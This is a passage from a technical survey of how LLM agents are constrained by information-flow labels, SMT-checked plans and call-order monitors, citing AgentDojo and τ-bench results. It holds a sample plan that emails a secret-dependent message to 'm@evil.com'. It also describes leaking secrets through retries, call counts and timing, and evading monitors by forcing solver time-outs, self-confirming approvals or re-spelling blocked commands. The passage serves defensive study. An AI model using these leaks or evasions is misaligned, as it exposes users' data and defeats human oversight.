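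Costa and colleagues' own system, FIDES, hides less from the planner. It keeps a label for the context and replaces a piece of a tool's result with a variable name only if that piece would raise the label. For example, the planner might see an email's date but only a name such as `#read_emails_0.body` in place of its text. The planner can pass this name to another tool, and the software inserts the text together with its label. Unlike CaMeL's planner, the FIDES planner can also open the variable, and the context then takes on the label of the contents.

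Costa and colleagues tested several designs on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed without an attack, and the number of attacks that succeeded in separate runs:

| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Chat | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 | 152 |
| One label for the context, with checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 | 0 |
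| Variables the planner can't open, with checks | 48.0 | 44.0 | 56.3 | 35.2 | 0 |
| FIDES, with checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 | 0 |

The attack counts exclude cases that AgentDojo scored as successful attacks but Costa and colleagues judged harmless, such as calls that the policy had blocked. Averaged over the four groups, FIDES completed about 50 percent of the tasks, the agent with one label completed about 42 percent, and the unprotected agent completed 84 percent. With the stronger model o1, FIDES's lead over the agent with one label grew to 16 percentage points. The travel tasks are an exception because the agent is allowed to call many of their tools even after reading untrusted text.

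The zeros depend on good labels. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, so the labels fitted the attacks exactly, whereas an operator has to guess where attackers can write. The test is also weak evidence about protecting secrets, because FIDES hid values only when they were untrusted and left confidentiality to the policies.

Later designs relax the separation between planner and data. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), the agent that reads the data may call tools itself, within the limits of its label, and returns a labelled result that the outer agent can pass on without reading. Garby and colleagues built an agent in a small programming language that labels every value. Their agent completed about as many of AgentDojo's banking tasks as CaMeL does without policy checks, even though their agent's checks were always on. Attacks succeeded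 in two of the 1,296 runs that were attacked.

### Releasing part of a secret

Hidden values are of little use if the system never releases anything derived from them, and the planner may need to know something about them to choose its next step. One way to declassify information about them is to allow only fixed-format answers. For example, FIDES can ask a quarantined model whether an inbox contains a meeting request and accept only true or false. It ranks answer formats by how much information they can carry, from true/false to a choice from a list to free text. A policy can then let the planner act on a true/false answer from untrusted mail, since one bit can't contain an instruction.

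An answer's format limits how much of a secret it can leak. A true/false answer reveals at most one bit, and a choice from eight options reveals at most three bits. But 256 true/false answers about different bits reveal all of a 256-bit key, so the monitor has to keep count of how much it has released about each secret. Costa and colleagues left fixed-format answers out of their AgentDojo tests. Garby and colleagues object that when such a value passes, nobody can tell from the run whether it was the intended release or a leak.

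The other common form is human approval. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), an agent called Prudentia extends FIDES by giving the planner the labels and policies, so that it can avoid steps that need approval. It can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data, meaning to declare it trustworthy. If an email lists ten errands, one endorsement replaces ten separate approvals. The results on AgentDojo with the model o3-mini were:

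| Agent | Tasks completed without approval | Approvals needed across completed tasks |
|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential action | 24.3% | 48.2 |
| One label for the context | 35.5% | 32.4 |
| FIDES | 50.1% | 18.8 |
| Prudentia | 59.1% | about 17 |

Kolluri and colleagues assumed that a person would approve every call a successful task needed and stop every attack. They didn't test this with people, and they share Meijer's concern that frequent prompts lead to careless approval. On WASP, a benchmark of attacks on agents that use websites, Prudentia stopped all attacks without asking for approval. The legitimate tasks in WASP are only posting a comment or upvoting a post, which an agent can do without reading what strangers wrote.

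Prudentia doesn't give users a general way to lower the secrecy of data. Kolluri and colleagues argue that whether a release is acceptable depends on the situation, so a person should approve the individual call. But a message containing only "yes" looks harmless to that person unless the approval prompt shows that the agent computed it from a key. In *SafeFlow*, a model may cite evidence, but its explanation can't remove a label.

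The policies in both FIDES and Prudentia also have a broader exception. An agent may send private data to anyone if it decided to do so before reading anything untrusted, on the assumption that the decision reflects the user's wishes. This condition stops an attacker who plants instructions, but it doesn't prevent the model from picking the wrong recipient by mistake.

### Comparing two runs

In 1982, Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined the standard that secrecy labels approximate. A system satisfies noninterference if changing the secret never changes what an observer sees. For a plan P with public input x, this means that for any two secrets s₁ and s₂,

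observe(P(x, s₁)) = observe(P(x, s₂))

Suppose an agent's plan sends one word, depending on the last bit of a key:

```
key = read_file("signing.key")
if last_bit(key) = 1:  send("yes")
else:                  send("no")
```

This is an implicit flow. Neither word carries a label, so a checker that follows only values reports no leak. The log of a single run doesn't reveal the leak either, because a run that sends "yes" looks the same as a run of a harmless plan that always sends "yes". A check has to compare two runs, because the leak is a difference between them.

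Gilles Barthe and colleagues described a way to do this in 2004, called self-composition. The formula contains two copies of the plan. They share the public inputs, but each has its own secret, and the solver looks for two secrets that lead to different observations. Here is the query for a key of eight bits, where `(_ BitVec 8)` is the type of eight-bit values and `extract` picks out bits:

```
(define-fun last-bit ((k (_ BitVec 8))) (_ BitVec 1)
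  ((_ extract 0 0) k))
(define-fun message ((k (_ BitVec 8))) String
  (ite (= (last-bit k) #b1) "yes" "no"))

(declare-const key1 (_ BitVec 8))      ; the key in one run
(declare-const key2 (_ BitVec 8))      ; the key in the other run
(assert (distinct (message key1) (message key2)))
(check-sat)                            ; sat: e.g. 00000000, 00000001

(assert (= (last-bit key1) (last-bit key2)))
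(check-sat)                            ; unsat
```

The counterexample is a pair of keys that differ only in the last bit. The final assertion declassifies that bit by limiting the query to pairs of keys that agree on it. The `unsat` answer then proves that the message reveals nothing else about the key. This is more exact than removing a label, because the policy states which fact the message may reveal.

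Girrens and Wang's rule, which labels both branches of a secret condition, also catches this leak but is stricter than noninterference. If both branches sent "done", the rule would still mark the message as secret, even though the two-run query would return `unsat`.

To include a language model, the formula can treat it as an uninterpreted function. Because models choose their words partly at random, the function takes the random choices as a second input, which is the same in both runs:

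```
(declare-fun llm (String Int) String)  ; context, random choices
(declare-const request String)
(declare-const r Int)
(declare-const secret1 String)
(declare-const secret2 String)

(push)
(assert (distinct (llm (str.++ request secret1) r)
                  (llm (str.++ request secret2) r)))
(check-sat)                            ; sat
(pop)

(assert (distinct (llm (str.++ request "#file_0") r)
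                  (llm (str.++ request "#file_0") r)))
(check-sat)                            ; unsat
```

The `sat` answer means that the formula doesn't rule out a leak, not that a real model would leak the secret. The cautious label rule follows from the same reasoning. In the last query, the model receives only a variable name, so its input is identical in both runs and its output must be too, which is the logical argument for hiding values from the planner.

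Self-composition is reliable only if the formula describes the two runs accurately. *PACE* (2026) notes that a tool's code may not describe which inputs the agent will choose for it. The formula contains those choices if the plan is fixed in advance, but if the agent decides each step as it goes, the formula has to allow for every choice the model might make.

### A leak through a branch that doesn't run

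Garby and colleagues found a leak in CaMeL that depends on when the system assigns labels. CaMeL blocks a plan that emails an outsider if the user's balance exceeds some threshold, because the condition reads the balance. Now consider a longer version, adapted from their example:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:                          rich = False
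if rich:                         send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and gets a secret label. The assignment `rich = False` then doesn't run, so `rich` stays true without a label and the email goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. The outsider can therefore tell whether the balance is high by whether the email arrives. A two-run query finds this leak with one balance on each side of the threshold. Labelling both branches before the plan runs also catches it.

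They also found that retries can leak secrets. Whether the policy blocks a run can depend on a secret, which reveals one bit. Most definitions of secure information flow allow this. The one that Garby and colleagues prove for their own language, for example, lets a program reveal something by failing to finish. But CaMeL runs inside an ordinary loop that retries after a failure, and no label covers that loop. An attacker who adapts each attempt to the last could extract the whole secret bit by bit. Girrens and Wang's verifier finishes its check before any tool runs, so the result can't depend on a value that a tool hasn't read yet.

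### Tool choice, call counts and timing

A noninterference proof covers only the observations in the formula. In an example from Tallam and Miller, a plan fetches a harmless address as many times as a secret number indicates:

```
for i in range(secret): fetch("ping")
```

The number of requests an agent sends to an address can reveal a secret even if the requests are identical and don't contain it, because the owner of the address can count them. The choice of tool can also reveal information, as can an error that occurs only for certain secrets. A two-run query can cover all of these if it compares the whole sequence of visible calls instead of only their contents. Timing is harder to cover because the formula would need to describe how long each tool call and model call takes.

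Tallam and Miller propose capping the number of repetitions, combining many calls into one, and making successful and failed steps follow the same path. When a loop depends on a secret, they would also block calls that change anything, or ask the user first. To prevent leaks through timing, they suggest padding sensitive steps to their longest duration or adding random delays, though an attacker can overcome random delays by taking more measurements. They don't test these measures on agents.

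Costa and colleagues deliberately accept such channels. FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, which covers data copied into a call but not what an observer can infer from which calls the agent makes. They argue that full noninterference would in effect forbid any publicly visible action after the agent has read a secret. Many ordinary requests would then fail. For example, a user may ask the agent to email the landlord if the account balance is too low to pay the rent. The email's arrival reveals something about the balance, as the user intends.

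Hiding untrusted text from the planner also makes these channels harder to exploit, since planted instructions can't add a loop or a revealing question to the plan. A plan written without an attacker's influence can still leak some data, perhaps one bit per run. That is tolerable for a plan that a user starts once. It is a greater risk for an agent that runs the same plan on every incoming email, because an outsider can trigger it thousands of times and vary the message each time.

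## Enforcing order: reading a file before editing it

A coding agent that edits a file without reading it has to guess what the file contains and may overwrite code it has never seen. A team can require the agent to read each file first, but neither a path check nor a taint label enforces that, because the file is inside the project and the edit moves no secret data. Whether `edit("b")` is acceptable depends only on what the agent did earlier.

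### What a monitor can enforce by stopping a run

*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) introduced security automata to describe rules of this kind. A security automaton has a set of states, and each state has a list of permitted actions and the next state each one leads to. A monitor tracks the current state as a program runs and stops the program if it requests an action that the state doesn't permit. Monitors for AI agents usually refuse the call instead and let the agent continue, which protects the file equally well.

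For a single file `b`, the automaton needs two states, "unread" and "read". In "unread", the agent may read `b`, which leads to "read", or do something unrelated to `b`, which leaves the state unchanged. "Unread" has no transition for editing `b`. In "read", the agent may do anything.

Schneider showed that a monitor that can only stop a run can enforce safety properties and no others. A safety property requires that nothing forbidden ever happens, and once a run breaks it, no continuation can repair the violation. The rule that an agent must read a file before editing it is a safety property, because reading the file after the edit doesn't repair the violation.

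This limit exists because the monitor sees only the actions so far. It must stop every rule-breaking run after finitely many actions, without stopping any run that could still satisfy the rule. It can do both only if every rule-breaking run reaches a point after which no further actions could satisfy the rule, which is the definition of a safety property. Basin et al. (2012) give access control based on past actions as an example, and reading a file before editing it is a rule of that type.

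A liveness property requires that something eventually happens, for instance that the agent later reads back every file it writes. Tripakis (2019), in *Safety and Liveness*, defines it by the condition

∀σ ∈ Σ\* ∃ρ ∈ Σ^ω : σ · ρ ∈ L

where L is the set of runs that satisfy the rule, σ is any finite sequence of actions and ρ is an infinite continuation. Whatever the agent has done so far, some continuation still satisfies the rule, so the monitor never has grounds to stop.

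Many rules combine safety and liveness. Alpern and Schneider (1985) proved in *Defining liveness* that every property is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property. For example, a rule might require the agent to read a file back after each write, before writing to it again. The safety part forbids a second write before the read. The liveness part also requires a read after the last write, which a monitor that can only stop the run cannot enforce.

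A monitor may be unable to enforce even a safety property if it doesn't control the action. When a colleague's text editor overwrites a file, the agent's monitor may detect the change but can't prevent it. Noninterference is neither a safety nor a liveness property, because it compares two runs, while those properties apply to each run separately.

### One record for each file

An automaton that tracks only whether the agent has read any file would let the agent read `a` and then edit `b`. Tracking two files takes four states: nothing read, only `a`, only `b`, or both. Each further file doubles the number, so 20 files require 1,048,576 states. A separate two-state automaton for each file is simpler. An ordinary program can store the states of these automata as a set of the file names read so far, and a formula can use an array R that maps each file name to true or false. Reading f sets R[f]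 to true, and editing f requires R[f] to be true.

Consider this plan, where `c` is a condition whose value nobody knows before the plan runs:

```
read a
if c:  read b
edit b
```

The query builds one copy of the array for each step and asks whether the edit can find `b` unread:

```
(define-sort Marks () (Array String Bool))
(define-fun nothing () Marks ((as const Marks) false))

(declare-const c Bool)
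(define-fun r1 () Marks (store nothing "a" true))        ; read a
(define-fun r2 () Marks (ite c (store r1 "b" true) r1))  ; if c: read b
(assert (not (select r2 "b")))                           ; edit b: unread
(check-sat)                                              ; sat: c = false
```

The solver returns `c` = false, the case in which the plan skips the read. The planner can repair the plan by reading `b` unconditionally or by making the edit depend on `c` too. With the second repair, the edit happens only when `c` is true, so the query also includes `(assert c)` and the solver returns `unsat`.

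The array `nothing` is false for every file name, which assumes that the agent has just started. If the agent has already been working, the monitor can fill the starting array from its log. An author can also leave the starting array unknown. The query for a plan that reads `b` and then edits it is still `unsat`, so the proof holds whatever the agent did before.

The author also has to decide what counts as a read. An attempt that ends in "file not found" shouldn't set R[f]. If the read tool can return part of a file, an agent that has seen the first 50 lines of 2,000 may pass the check and edit line 1,800. A stricter formula would record which lines the agent has read.

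### Unknown names and changing contents

File names are often unknown when the solver checks a plan. Suppose a plan reads the file `p` that a search returns and edits the file `q` that a settings file names. The planner expects them to be the same file. With `Marks` and `nothing` defined as before, the query is:

```
(declare-const p String)               ; the file the plan reads
(declare-const q String)               ; the file the plan edits
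(define-fun r () Marks (store nothing p true))
(assert (not (select r q)))
(check-sat)                            ; sat: e.g. p = "a", q = "b"
```

(assert (= p q))
(check-sat)                            ; unsat
```

The solver finds a violation of the rule by giving the two variables different values. That could happen in practice, for example if the search finds a `config.yaml` in the wrong directory. The plan should use one variable for both calls or compare the names before the edit.

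Two different strings can also name one file, through links or a `..` segment. The file then counts as unread under its second name, and the agent has to make an unnecessary but harmless call to read it again. It is dangerous when a file's contents change but its name doesn't. Suppose the agent reads `b` and a colleague then saves a new version. R[b] is still true, so the agent can edit `b` based on the old text.

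A version number catches this. Let now[f] be the current version of f and seen[f] the version that the agent last read, with −1 for a file it has never read. Every write, by anyone, raises now[f] by one. An edit requires

seen[f] = now[f]

If a plan reads `b` and then edits it, the solver can now find a violation in which a colleague saves the file between the two calls. No plan can prevent that save, so the edit tool should make the comparison.

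Ordinary files have no version counter, so the tool can store a hash (a short fingerprint of the contents) or the time of the last change. A hash won't reveal a change that someone has since undone, but this is harmless because the agent has already seen the restored contents. A timestamp can miss a second save if it comes so soon after the first that the clock records the same time for both. After a successful edit, the tool should update seen[f], or the agent will have to reread the file before editing it again. The tool must also block other writes between the comparison and its own write, or there will again be a race between checking and writing.

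### From k calls to any number of calls

A plan fixes the calls in advance, but a monitor has to work for any sequence that an agent requests. Bounded model checking asks a solver whether any run of at most k steps breaks a rule. The formula contains a copy of the state for each step:

Init(x₀) ∧ Step(x₀, x₁) ∧ … ∧ Step(xₖ₋₁, xₖ) ∧ (Bad(x₀) ∨ … ∨ Bad(xₖ))

Here xᵢ is the state after i calls, including the latest call. Init describes the start, Step describes what one call may do, and Bad describes the states that break the rule. The solver chooses the tools and file names itself.

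Suppose a monitor keeps the array R for an agent with read, edit and copy tools. As with paths, the query also needs to track the truth independently of the monitor, in this case what the agent has seen. Let S[f] be true if the agent has seen the current contents of f. Copying `b` over `a` gives `a` the contents of `b`, so S[a] takes the value of S[b], but the monitor mistakenly leaves R unchanged. A state is bad if the monitor has just allowed an edit of a file whose current contents the agent hasn't seen.

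For k = 2 the solver returns `unsat`. For k = 3 it finds this run:

| Call | R, the monitor's record | S, contents the agent has seen |
|---|---|---|
| `read a` | `a` | `a` |
| copy `b` over `a` | `a` | none |
| `edit a` | `a`, so the monitor allows it | none, so the edit breaks the rule |

An `unsat` answer for k calls doesn't rule out a violation at call k + 1. If a plan has no loops, setting k to the length of its longest path covers every call. An agent that chooses each step as it goes has no longest path, and raising k makes the formula larger.

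Induction removes the bound, as it did for the depth counter in file paths. The invariant for this rule is

for every file f: R[f] ⇒ S[f]

In words, the monitor has a file on record only if the agent has seen its current contents. At the start R is empty, so the invariant holds. It also implies the rule, since the monitor allows an edit only when R[f] is true. What remains is to show that no call breaks it. Here is the query for copying, first with the forgetful monitor and then with a repaired one:

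```
(declare-const r Marks)                ; R before the call
(declare-const s Marks)                ; S before the call
(declare-const src String)
(declare-const dst String)
(declare-const x String)               ; a file that breaks the invariant

(assert (=> (select r x) (select s x)))        ; invariant for x
(assert (=> (select r src) (select s src)))    ; invariant for src
(define-fun s2 () Marks (store s dst (select s src)))
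(assert (not (select s2 x)))

(push)
(assert (select r x))                  ; the monitor ignores the copy
(check-sat)                            ; sat: x = dst
(pop)

(define-fun r2 () Marks (store r dst (select r src)))
(assert (select r2 x))                 ; the monitor copies the record too
(check-sat)                            ; unsat
```

The query assumes the invariant only for `x` and `src`, because no other file affects the outcome. The repaired monitor gives the copy the same record as the original, much as a taint label follows copied data. Reading sets both R[f] and S[f] to true. Editing changes neither, because the agent wrote the change itself. All three tools preserve the invariant, so the rule holds after any number of calls.

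The proof covers only the tools that the formula describes. If a shell command or a colleague's save overwrites `a`, S[a] becomes false but R[a] stays true. With version numbers, the invariant becomes that if seen[f] = now[f], the agent has seen the current contents of f. Any write that raises now[f] preserves this invariant.

An induction query can return `sat` even when the monitor is correct, because the solver may start from a state that satisfies the invariant but that no real run reaches. In that case, the author needs a stronger invariant. A bounded search from the real starting state can help determine whether the fault is real. Here, the run of three calls confirms that it is.

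### Agentproof and CaMeLoT: order in a graph

Two recent systems check the order of actions before an agent runs, without an SMT solver. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) analyses the workflow graphs in which developers define an agent's possible steps. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) analyses the plans that CaMeL's privileged model writes. A third system, Agent-C, uses the SMT solver Z3 to check each call as the model generates it (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025, *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*).

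| | Agentproof | CaMeLoT | Agent-C |
|---|---|---|---|
| What it checks | A workflow, before deployment | A plan, before it runs | Each call, before it runs |
| Method | Graph combined with a finite automaton | The model checker nuXmv | The SMT solver Z3 |
| Can tell file `a` from file `b` | No | No | Yes |
| Takes branch conditions into account | No | No | Not needed, as the branch is already known |
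| Main tests | 18 workflows, 15 rules | 97 AgentDojo tasks and a set of security plans | 165 τ-bench tasks and 34 attacks |

Agentproof reads the graph from four common libraries for building agents, including LangGraph and CrewAI. It turns each rule into a finite automaton and explores pairs of a graph node and an automaton state, following every outgoing edge from each pair. If it reaches a pair whose automaton state means "violated", the path to that pair is a counterexample. The number of pairs is at most the number of nodes times the number of states, and in the experiments it never exceeded 24.

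Xavier and colleagues wrote the 18 workflows themselves and included known mistakes. Agentproof found structural faults in five of them, such as a dead-end step, and ten had no human approval step. These counts show that the tool finds such faults, but not how common they are in practice. The search also found a missing human review in one workflow after ten random runs had failed to reveal it, which is more telling than the counts.

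Reading before editing is hard to state in Agentproof's rule language, which has no operators for past steps. The rule `a -> F b` means that b must follow a. One of the 15 test rules, "Deploy approval", is `tool:deploy -> F tool:approve`, which requires approval after the deployment. According to the transitions Xavier and colleagues list, its automaton reports an error only when a second deployment comes before the approval. A single deployment that nobody ever approves passes, because the automaton enforces only the safety part of the rule and not the liveness part, which requires that approval eventually happens.

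Another of Agentproof's checks tests order correctly. To check that a person always approves before a sensitive tool runs, it removes the approval steps from the graph and searches for a path to that tool. Any path it finds bypasses approval. The same method could check that a read comes before every edit, by removing the read steps and searching for a path to the edit step. But the nodes carry tool names without arguments, so reading `a` would count as reading `b` unless each file had its own node.

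CaMeLoT translates a plan into a finite-state machine and passes it to nuXmv, a program that checks all runs of such a machine. The rules use computation tree logic (CTL), a branching-time logic, which can describe the different futures open from one state. AG p means that p holds in every state on every path, and AF p means that p eventually holds on every path. A[p U q] means that on every path q eventually holds, and p holds until then. In this notation, one could write the rule about reading in two ways:

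AG(call_edit ⇒ read_called)

A[¬call_edit U read_called]

Both versions reject a plan that edits the file before reading it. The version with U also requires a read on every path through the plan, so it rejects a plan that reads and edits the file in one branch and finishes without touching it in the other. Nikolaou and colleagues use the U form for a rule that an agent must confirm which computer is affected before cutting it off from the network, so their formula would reject a plan that skips both steps when the alarm turns out to be false.

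The variable `read_called` becomes true when the plan calls the tool and then stays true, like the array R with a single entry. CaMeLoT does not model the values of arguments, so a plan that confirms workstation 17 and then cuts off workstation 18 would satisfy the confirmation rule. It also assumes that either side of a branch can be taken, regardless of earlier branches. Like the graph search for leaks, it would reject a safe plan that reads `b` only if a condition holds and later edits it under the same condition.

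In one test, Nikolaou and colleagues altered a safe plan for responding to security alerts in seven ways, each breaking one rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one, which is unsurprising because they had chosen rules that CaMeL cannot naturally express. On AgentDojo, with Claude Haiku 4.5 as the planner, the plans for 22 of the 97 tasks failed to do what the user wanted under either system. CaMeL and CaMeLoT agreed on 59 of the other 75, passing 42 plans and blocking 17. Most disagreements involved facts known only at run time, such as who may read a file.

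CaMeLoT can also derive requirements from the user's request, such as that a message must be sent. The language model fills in one of ten templates, and ordinary code turns the template into CTL. This produced valid formulas for all 97 tasks. When the models wrote CTL directly, GPT-4.1 nano produced valid formulas for only 12 tasks and Claude Haiku 4.5 for 96, so the templates mainly help weaker models.

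### Agent-C: checking a call as the model writes it

In Agent-C's rule language, reading before editing looks like this:

```
Before(edit(file = f1), True, read(file = f2), f1 == f2)
```

Agent-C translates the rule into a formula about the trace, the list of calls so far:

∀t. tool(t) = edit ⇒ ∃t′ < t. tool(t′) = read ∧ file(t′) = file(t)

Without the condition `f1 == f2`, reading any file would permit editing any other. The rule can also refer to the earlier call's output, so it can exclude reads that failed.

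When the model has generated a complete call, Agent-C adds it to the trace and uses Z3 to check whether the trace and the rules can be true together, with all future calls left open. It allows the new call only if the result is `sat`. Winston and colleagues' monitor also relied on `sat`, and it allowed the cancellation of a 30-hour-old booking. Agent-C avoids that loophole for rules about earlier calls because it fixes those calls to their recorded values, so the solver can choose values only for future calls.

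This query can detect that an action would make the rules impossible to satisfy together, even if it breaks none of them individually. Suppose the agent must read back every file it writes, and must not read any files after sending its report. It has written `b` but not read it back, and now tries to send the report. Sending it would break neither rule immediately, but the agent could then no longer read `b` as the first rule requires without breaking the second. Z3 therefore returns `unsat`, and Agent-C refuses the call. A monitor that checked each rule separately would allow it.

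After a refusal, Agent-C discards an open-weight model's output back to the tool name and generates another call from there. Commercial providers don't expose the probabilities this requires, so with their models Agent-C has to send the whole prompt again. In tests with Qwen3-8B, the agent succeeded at 42.1 percent of the shop tasks when Agent-C went back to the tool name, compared with 36.5 percent when it sent the prompt again. Going back to the tool name also discarded only about 18 tokens each time the agent ran the model, instead of 257.

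Kamath and colleagues tested Agent-C on 115 shop tasks and 50 airline tasks from τ-bench. "Obeyed" is the percentage of tasks without a violation, and "success" is the percentage that the agent also completed:

| Model | Safeguard | Shop: obeyed | Shop: success | Airline: obeyed | Airline: success |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-32B | None | 37.7 | 25.5 | 35.3 | 17.3 |
| Qwen3-32B | AgentSpec | 84.1 | 37.4 | 79.3 | 38.7 |
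| Qwen3-32B | Agent-C | 100 | 53.3 | 100 | 35.8 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | None | 93.0 | 76.5 | 70.0 | 42.0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | Agent-C | 100 | 80.5 | 100 | 43.5 |
| GPT-5 | None | 91.9 | 71.0 | 71.3 | 38.0 |
| GPT-5 | Agent-C | 100 | 73.6 | 100 | 42.8 |

Agent-C more than doubled the success rate of the weaker model but added at most about five percentage points for the two stronger ones. On the airline tasks, the ordinary monitor AgentSpec did slightly better than Agent-C. Strong models benefited most clearly in tests where the user tried to obtain something forbidden. Without any checks, Claude Sonnet 4.5 carried out the harmful action in 5 of 17 such shop tasks. With Agent-C, no model carried out a harmful action in any test. The checks increased the average task time with Qwen3-32B from 333 to 480 seconds.

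As with Soteria, the scores of 100 percent follow from the design and don't show that the formulas match the written policy. The shop's policy allows refunds to the original payment method or to an existing gift card in the customer's account. The formula that Kamath and colleagues print accepts any payment method whose name contains `gift_card`, so the refund tool has to reject a card that doesn't exist or belongs to someone else.

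Confirmation is a second weak point. Kamath and colleagues added a tool called `action_confirmed` that records the user's approval in the trace. If the model calls this tool without asking the user, the trace still satisfies a rule that requires approval before a change. Yu and colleagues' monitor avoids this by taking approvals only from the user's messages.

### When a lookup table is enough

For a single call with a known path, the entire check fits in a few lines of ordinary code:

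```
if tool == "read" and succeeded:  seen.add(path)
if tool == "edit" and path not in seen:  refuse
```

For rules about past calls, this table gives the same answers as Agent-C's solver, and it is faster and easy to read. A plan with literal file names and no branches doesn't need a solver either, since a program can check each step against the same table. When a rule mentions a few tools and no arguments, running an automaton over the workflow graph checks every path, though it raises some false alarms.

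A solver is useful for checking plans with unknown names or related branch conditions, and for finding rules that together leave the agent no way to finish. It can also prove that the monitor's table works for every sequence of calls, as in the case of copying. A team can do the proof once, when it writes the monitor, and then run only the table.

### Reading a file back after writing it

Some teams also want the agent to read a file after writing it, because a tool may cut off a long text or save it in the wrong encoding. This is a liveness rule, and a monitor cannot enforce it by blocking calls. After the agent writes `b`, no later call breaks the rule, because the read may still follow. Stopping the run would guarantee that the read never happens. If the model tries to finish before reading the file, Agent-C ends the run with an error, and the file remains unchecked.

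A plan check can require the read before anything runs. Let the array P record which files await a read. Writing f sets P[f] to true, and reading f sets it to false. When the plan ends, P[f] must be false for every file. For a plan that writes `b` and then reads it only if `ok` is true, the solver returns `ok` = false. In CTL, the rule is

AG(call_write ⇒ AF call_read)

CaMeLoT uses this pattern for a rule that the agent must eventually resolve or escalate every incident ticket it opens. Loops complicate the check. A plan that writes a file, loops through a list and then reads the file will fail if the state machine may repeat the loop forever, because in one possible run the agent never reaches the read. The checker has to assume that loops finish, or prove it separately.

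Even after a successful check, the agent may depart from the plan, or the program may crash after the write.

Adding a deadline turns the rule into a safety property. In Agentproof's language, `write -> F[<=3] read` requires a read within three steps of a write. If the agent hasn't read the file by the last allowed step, a monitor can refuse any other call. The strictest deadline is one step, which means the agent's next call after writing a file must be to read it. But an agent that makes no further calls never reaches the deadline.

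Schneider's limit applies to monitors that can only stop a run. A monitor that can also insert actions can enforce some rules beyond safety properties, and here it could read the file after each write. The write tool can also return the stored contents as its result, which gives the model the text without a separate call but does not guarantee that it will detect that half the file is missing.

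## Running the solver: time-outs, unknown answers and solver errors

While an agent is running, the solver may take too long, return `unknown`, crash or, rarely, give a wrong answer. In each case, the monitor still has to decide what to do with the tool call.

### A decision for each answer

For a query that searches for a violation, the code in Z3's Python interface is short:

```
solver = Solver()
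solver.set("timeout", 2000)               # milliseconds
solver.add(facts, guards, violation)
answer = solver.check()

if answer == unsat:  permit(call)
elif answer == sat:  block(call, explain(solver.model()))
else:                block(call, solver.reason_unknown())
```

The last branch handles `unknown`, including time-outs. A programmer might shorten the code to "block if the answer is `sat`, otherwise permit". The shortened code would probably pass its tests, because test queries tend to be easy, but it would let every undecided call through. An attacker who can choose a file name could look for one that makes the query time out. If `unknown` blocks the call, the attacker can only stop the agent from working. A monitor that checks whether a call is consistent with the policy swaps the first two branches and keeps the third.

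Blocking undecided calls also affects legitimate users. AWS's tool Zelkova checks whether an access policy makes stored files public. If its solvers don't finish within 30 seconds, AWS treats the files as public and locks them, so people can lose access even though nobody changed a setting. Instead of blocking the call, an agent's monitor can ask a person or, if the undecided query was about a plan, wait until the arguments are known and check each call with ordinary code.

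The software that runs the solver should also enforce the time limit. *Sequent-Prover* (2026) describes an agent that calls Z3 as a tool. The surrounding software stops Z3 after 30 seconds, caps its memory at 256 megabytes, and returns the verdict, the full output and any error message in separate fields.

When Z3 can't parse an assertion, it normally reports an error, skips the assertion and answers for the rest of the script. Removing an assertion can only add solutions. If the monitor permits calls on `unsat`, a missing assertion can therefore block an allowed call but can't let a forbidden one through. If it permits calls on `sat`, a typing error in a rule can let a forbidden call through. The monitor should therefore block the call whenever the output contains an error.

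### Explaining a refusal

A counterexample gives the agent something specific to fix. For the plan that reads file `p` and edits file `q`, the monitor could report that the edit may change an unread file, for instance if the search returns `a` and the settings file names `b`. The monitor should leave out the arrays and helper variables in the raw output.

When `unsat` means "blocked", there is no counterexample, and the explanation comes from an unsatisfiable core. In this query, an agent wants to pay 250 to a new payee. The notation `(! … :named n)` gives an assertion a name:

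```
(set-option :produce-unsat-cores true)
(declare-const amount Int)
(declare-const approved Bool)
(declare-const new-payee Bool)
(assert (! (=> (> amount 300) approved) :named large-needs-approval))
(assert (! (=> new-payee (<= amount 100)) :named new-payee-limit))
(assert (! (= amount 250) :named amount-requested))
(assert (! new-payee :named payee-is-new))
(assert (! (not approved) :named no-approval))
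(check-sat)            ; unsat
(get-unsat-core)       ; new-payee-limit, amount-requested, payee-is-new
```

The core doesn't include the approval rule, so the agent can see that asking for approval won't help. If the amount were 400, the payment would break both rules, but the core might list only one of them. If it listed only the approval rule, the agent could obtain approval, try again and then fail on the limit for new payees.

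A core may contain assertions that aren't necessary for the conflict, and some solver configurations can't produce a core at all. *Quantifying Cross-Query Contradictions in Multi-Query LLM Reasoning* (2026) uses cores to find which of a language model's answers contradict each other. Where cores are unavailable, the paper's method removes constraints one at a time and solves again. If the remaining assertions still contradict each other, the removed one wasn't necessary for the conflict. Testing the five assertions above this way takes five solver calls.

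The explanation enters the model's context, so it shouldn't contain text that an attacker wrote. Rule names are safe to return because the developer chose them. A counterexample may include a file name or a line from an invoice, which the monitor can replace with a reference such as "the second argument".

### Why retries need a limit

*Loop Invariant Generation* (2025) describes this kind of feedback for a related task. A language model proposes an invariant for a program, and Z3 searches for a counterexample. The next prompt contains the counterexample and an instruction to rule it out. If the proposal has a syntax error, the prompt contains Z3's error message instead.

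Retrying doesn't necessarily produce a better result. In *Verifiable LLM-Guided Focal SMT Solving for Quantified Arrays* (2026), a model helps a solver with difficult formulas, but its proposals may be invalid or repeat earlier ones. The system therefore stops after a fixed number of rounds and runs an ordinary solver for the remaining time. Other systems also limit attempts. *Sequent-Prover* allows 10 turns, Soteria's planner had up to eight retries, and Winston and colleagues' agent had three.

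Every retry a monitor allows also gives the agent another chance to find a gap in the rules. For example, if the monitor refuses a deletion, the agent may try a spelling of the command that the rule doesn't match. After the last retry, the call should stay blocked until a person has looked at it.

### What makes a query hard

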